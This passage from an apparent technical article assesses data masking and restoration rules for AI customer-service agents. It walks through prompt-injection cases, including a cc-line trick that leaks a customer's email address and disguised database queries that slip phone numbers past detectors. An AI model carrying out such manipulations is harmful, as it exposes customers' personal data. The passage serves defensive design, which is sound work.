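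Hidet's example policy allows email addresses in the "to", "cc" and "bcc" fields. If the shop copied this policy, the stranger could ask for an email to [EMAIL_2], the stranger's own address, with [EMAIL_1], Maria's address, on the "cc" line. The vault would restore both because they are email addresses in approved fields. The stranger would then receive an email showing Maria's real address.

The rules in these examples limit the type of data, the tool and the field, but not the recipient. To prevent the "cc" attack, the shop also needs an argument constraint like the one in the policy for ticket 8812, which allows email only to the address on the customer's record. The placeholder [EMAIL_2] doesn't show whose address it is, so the enforcement point must either check the constraint after the real address is restored, just before the tool runs, or be able to look the address up.

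Whether to restore [PHONE_1] is therefore a permission decision. The protected resource is a row of the mapping table, and the rule sets which tool may receive it, in which field and for whom. Someone has to write these rules, and they interfere with legitimate work, as other permission rules do. If a courier needs Maria's number to arrange a return, the email to the courier will fail until the shop adds a rule for couriers.

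Session length also affects the risk. Hidet's server keeps one vault session open for the whole MCP connection, and a placeholder works only within its own session. If the shop opens a new connection for each ticket, a manipulated agent can misuse only the details it has met on that ticket. If one connection stays open all day, the agent can misuse the details of every customer it has met that day. Hidet's example policy also caps restoration at 50 values per step, which would slow the theft of a long list, though an agent might spread the list over several steps. Hidet reports 239 software tests of the library but no experiment with a manipulated agent.

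Software that operates websites can identify the recipient by the page's address. In an earlier version, Browser Use, a library for browser agents, let developers tie a password placeholder to a named site and advised them to limit which sites the agent could visit. In the current version, according to Browser Use, the model asks for a secret by name and the software types it in. If the secret belongs to one site, the software checks the address of the exact part of the page that will receive the keystrokes. It gets this address from the browser, because a malicious page could supply a false one, and types nothing if it can't establish the address.

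The same documentation warns that this "is not a sandbox". The secrets are in the process that runs the model's code, so code the model writes can read them. The model may also see a typed value in a screenshot. The first warning applies to any design in which the model writes programs that handle placeholders, including the one Anthropic described for copying contact details. Restoration rules protect little if a manipulated model's program can open the mapping table.

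For the most sensitive values, a person could approve each use. *SUDP* (2026) treats an agent's use of secrets as a confused-deputy problem and ties the user's approval to one operation, much as a bank asks a customer to confirm a particular payee and amount. The approval gives the agent no authority that an attacker could get it to use again. Asking for approval each time would be reasonable for a bank password, but not for every reply to a customer.

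### Stealing the mapping table

An attacker could also target the table. In Ma and colleagues' design, each placeholder is a random code that contains no personal data and works only in one session. The table stays out of prompts, search indexes and ordinary logs. Ma and colleagues gave a simulated attacker progressively more access and measured the share of protected values it could recover.

| What the attacker obtains | Values recovered from the targeted session | Values recovered from other sessions |
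|---|---|---|
| The placeholders | 0% | 0% |
| The audit log | 0% | 0% |
| Half of one session's table | 50% | 0% |
| All of one session's table | 100% | 0% |
| One session's restoration credential | 100% | 0% |
| The master seed | 100% | 100% |

All sessions depend on the master seed for protection, so losing it exposes every session, while reading one session's table exposes only that session. Ma and colleagues derived these percentages by analyzing the design of a reference version, not by measuring a working deployment. They recommend storing the master key in hardened hardware or a dedicated secrets manager, using short-lived credentials for restoration, and deleting tables promptly when a task ends.

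How much one session exposes depends on how the shop uses the agent. A table for Maria's ticket contains one customer's details, while a table for the manager's summary of 500 complaints could contain hundreds. A thief would also find more in a table kept for an agent with a long memory.

Encrypting the table does not protect against a manipulated agent. The agent does not need to steal the table, because the client decrypts the matching row whenever a tool call contains a placeholder.

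### Disguised data and planted instructions

All of this assumes that the detector found the data. Ma and colleagues disguised personal values in 200 documents in eight ways and measured how often detectors missed values they had previously caught. Inserting invisible characters hid 99.7% of these values from a detector that used simple rules. A small trained detector did much better, missing less than 1% under six of the eight disguises. However, it missed 18.4% of values when capital and small letters were swapped, and 28.2% of identifiers when their digits were spelled out as words. Converting text to a standard form before the search would be a simple improvement, though they didn't test it.

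An outsider can't change how the shop stores Maria's number, but a manipulated agent might be able to retrieve it in a different form. If the agent has a tool that accepts database queries, an attacker could use planted text to instruct it to request phone numbers with a letter between the digits, and the detector might miss them. The model could then rebuild the numbers and send them out with no placeholder for a restoration rule to check. Browser Use guards against some such tricks by also removing secrets that appear reversed or in common encodings. Where masking has worked, the attacker can't use this trick to get the number out, because the model sees only [PHONE_1] and has no digits to disguise.

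Masking also leaves planted instructions in place. A sentence telling the agent to refund a stranger's order may contain no personal data, so even a perfect detector would pass it on unchanged. Ma and colleagues say their system does not defend against such instructions.

Removing instructions requires a separate filter. *SPILLWAY* (2026) describes one that rewrites tool results using fixed rules. It removes text made to look like a message from the user or the system, sentences that address the agent about its task, and claims that a payee's bank account has changed. Some of its rules match the exact wording of the benchmark's attacks, so a good score there is weak evidence that it would catch other wordings. The filter would also remove a genuine notice from a supplier that had changed banks. *SPILLWAY* adds a separate check that blocks harmful actions if an instruction gets through the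 filter.

The table shows what each control does against the attacks a shop might face. The last column covers limits on tools, records and arguments. Tracking where data came from, as FIDES and CaMeL do, could stop some of the same leaks.

| Attacker's goal | Masking, with every placeholder restored | Masking, with restoration limited by rules | Limits on tools, records and arguments |
|---|---|---|---|
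| The provider reads a customer's phone number | Prevents it if the detector finds the number | Prevents it if the detector finds the number | Reduce the number of records the provider receives |
| The provider works out who wrote a masked complaint | Helps little if job, town and age remain | Helps little if job, town and age remain | Reduce the number of complaints the provider receives |
| An outsider gets the agent to send a customer's phone number | Doesn't prevent it | Prevents it unless the rules allow that field and recipient | Prevent it if email can go only to the address on record |
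| An outsider gets the agent to send the text of a complaint | Doesn't prevent it | Withholds the identifiers but not the story | Prevent it if email can go only to the address on record |
| An outsider gets the agent to fetch data in a disguised form | May miss the data | May miss the data | Prevent it if the agent can't write its own queries |
| An outsider gets the agent to issue a refund | Doesn't prevent it | Doesn't prevent it | Cap the loss, or prevent it if the agent has no refund tool |
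| A thief reads one session's mapping table | Exposes that session's values | Exposes that session's values | Reduce the number of customers in the table |
| A thief obtains the master seed | Exposes every session's values | Exposes every session's values | Reduce the number of customers in the tables |
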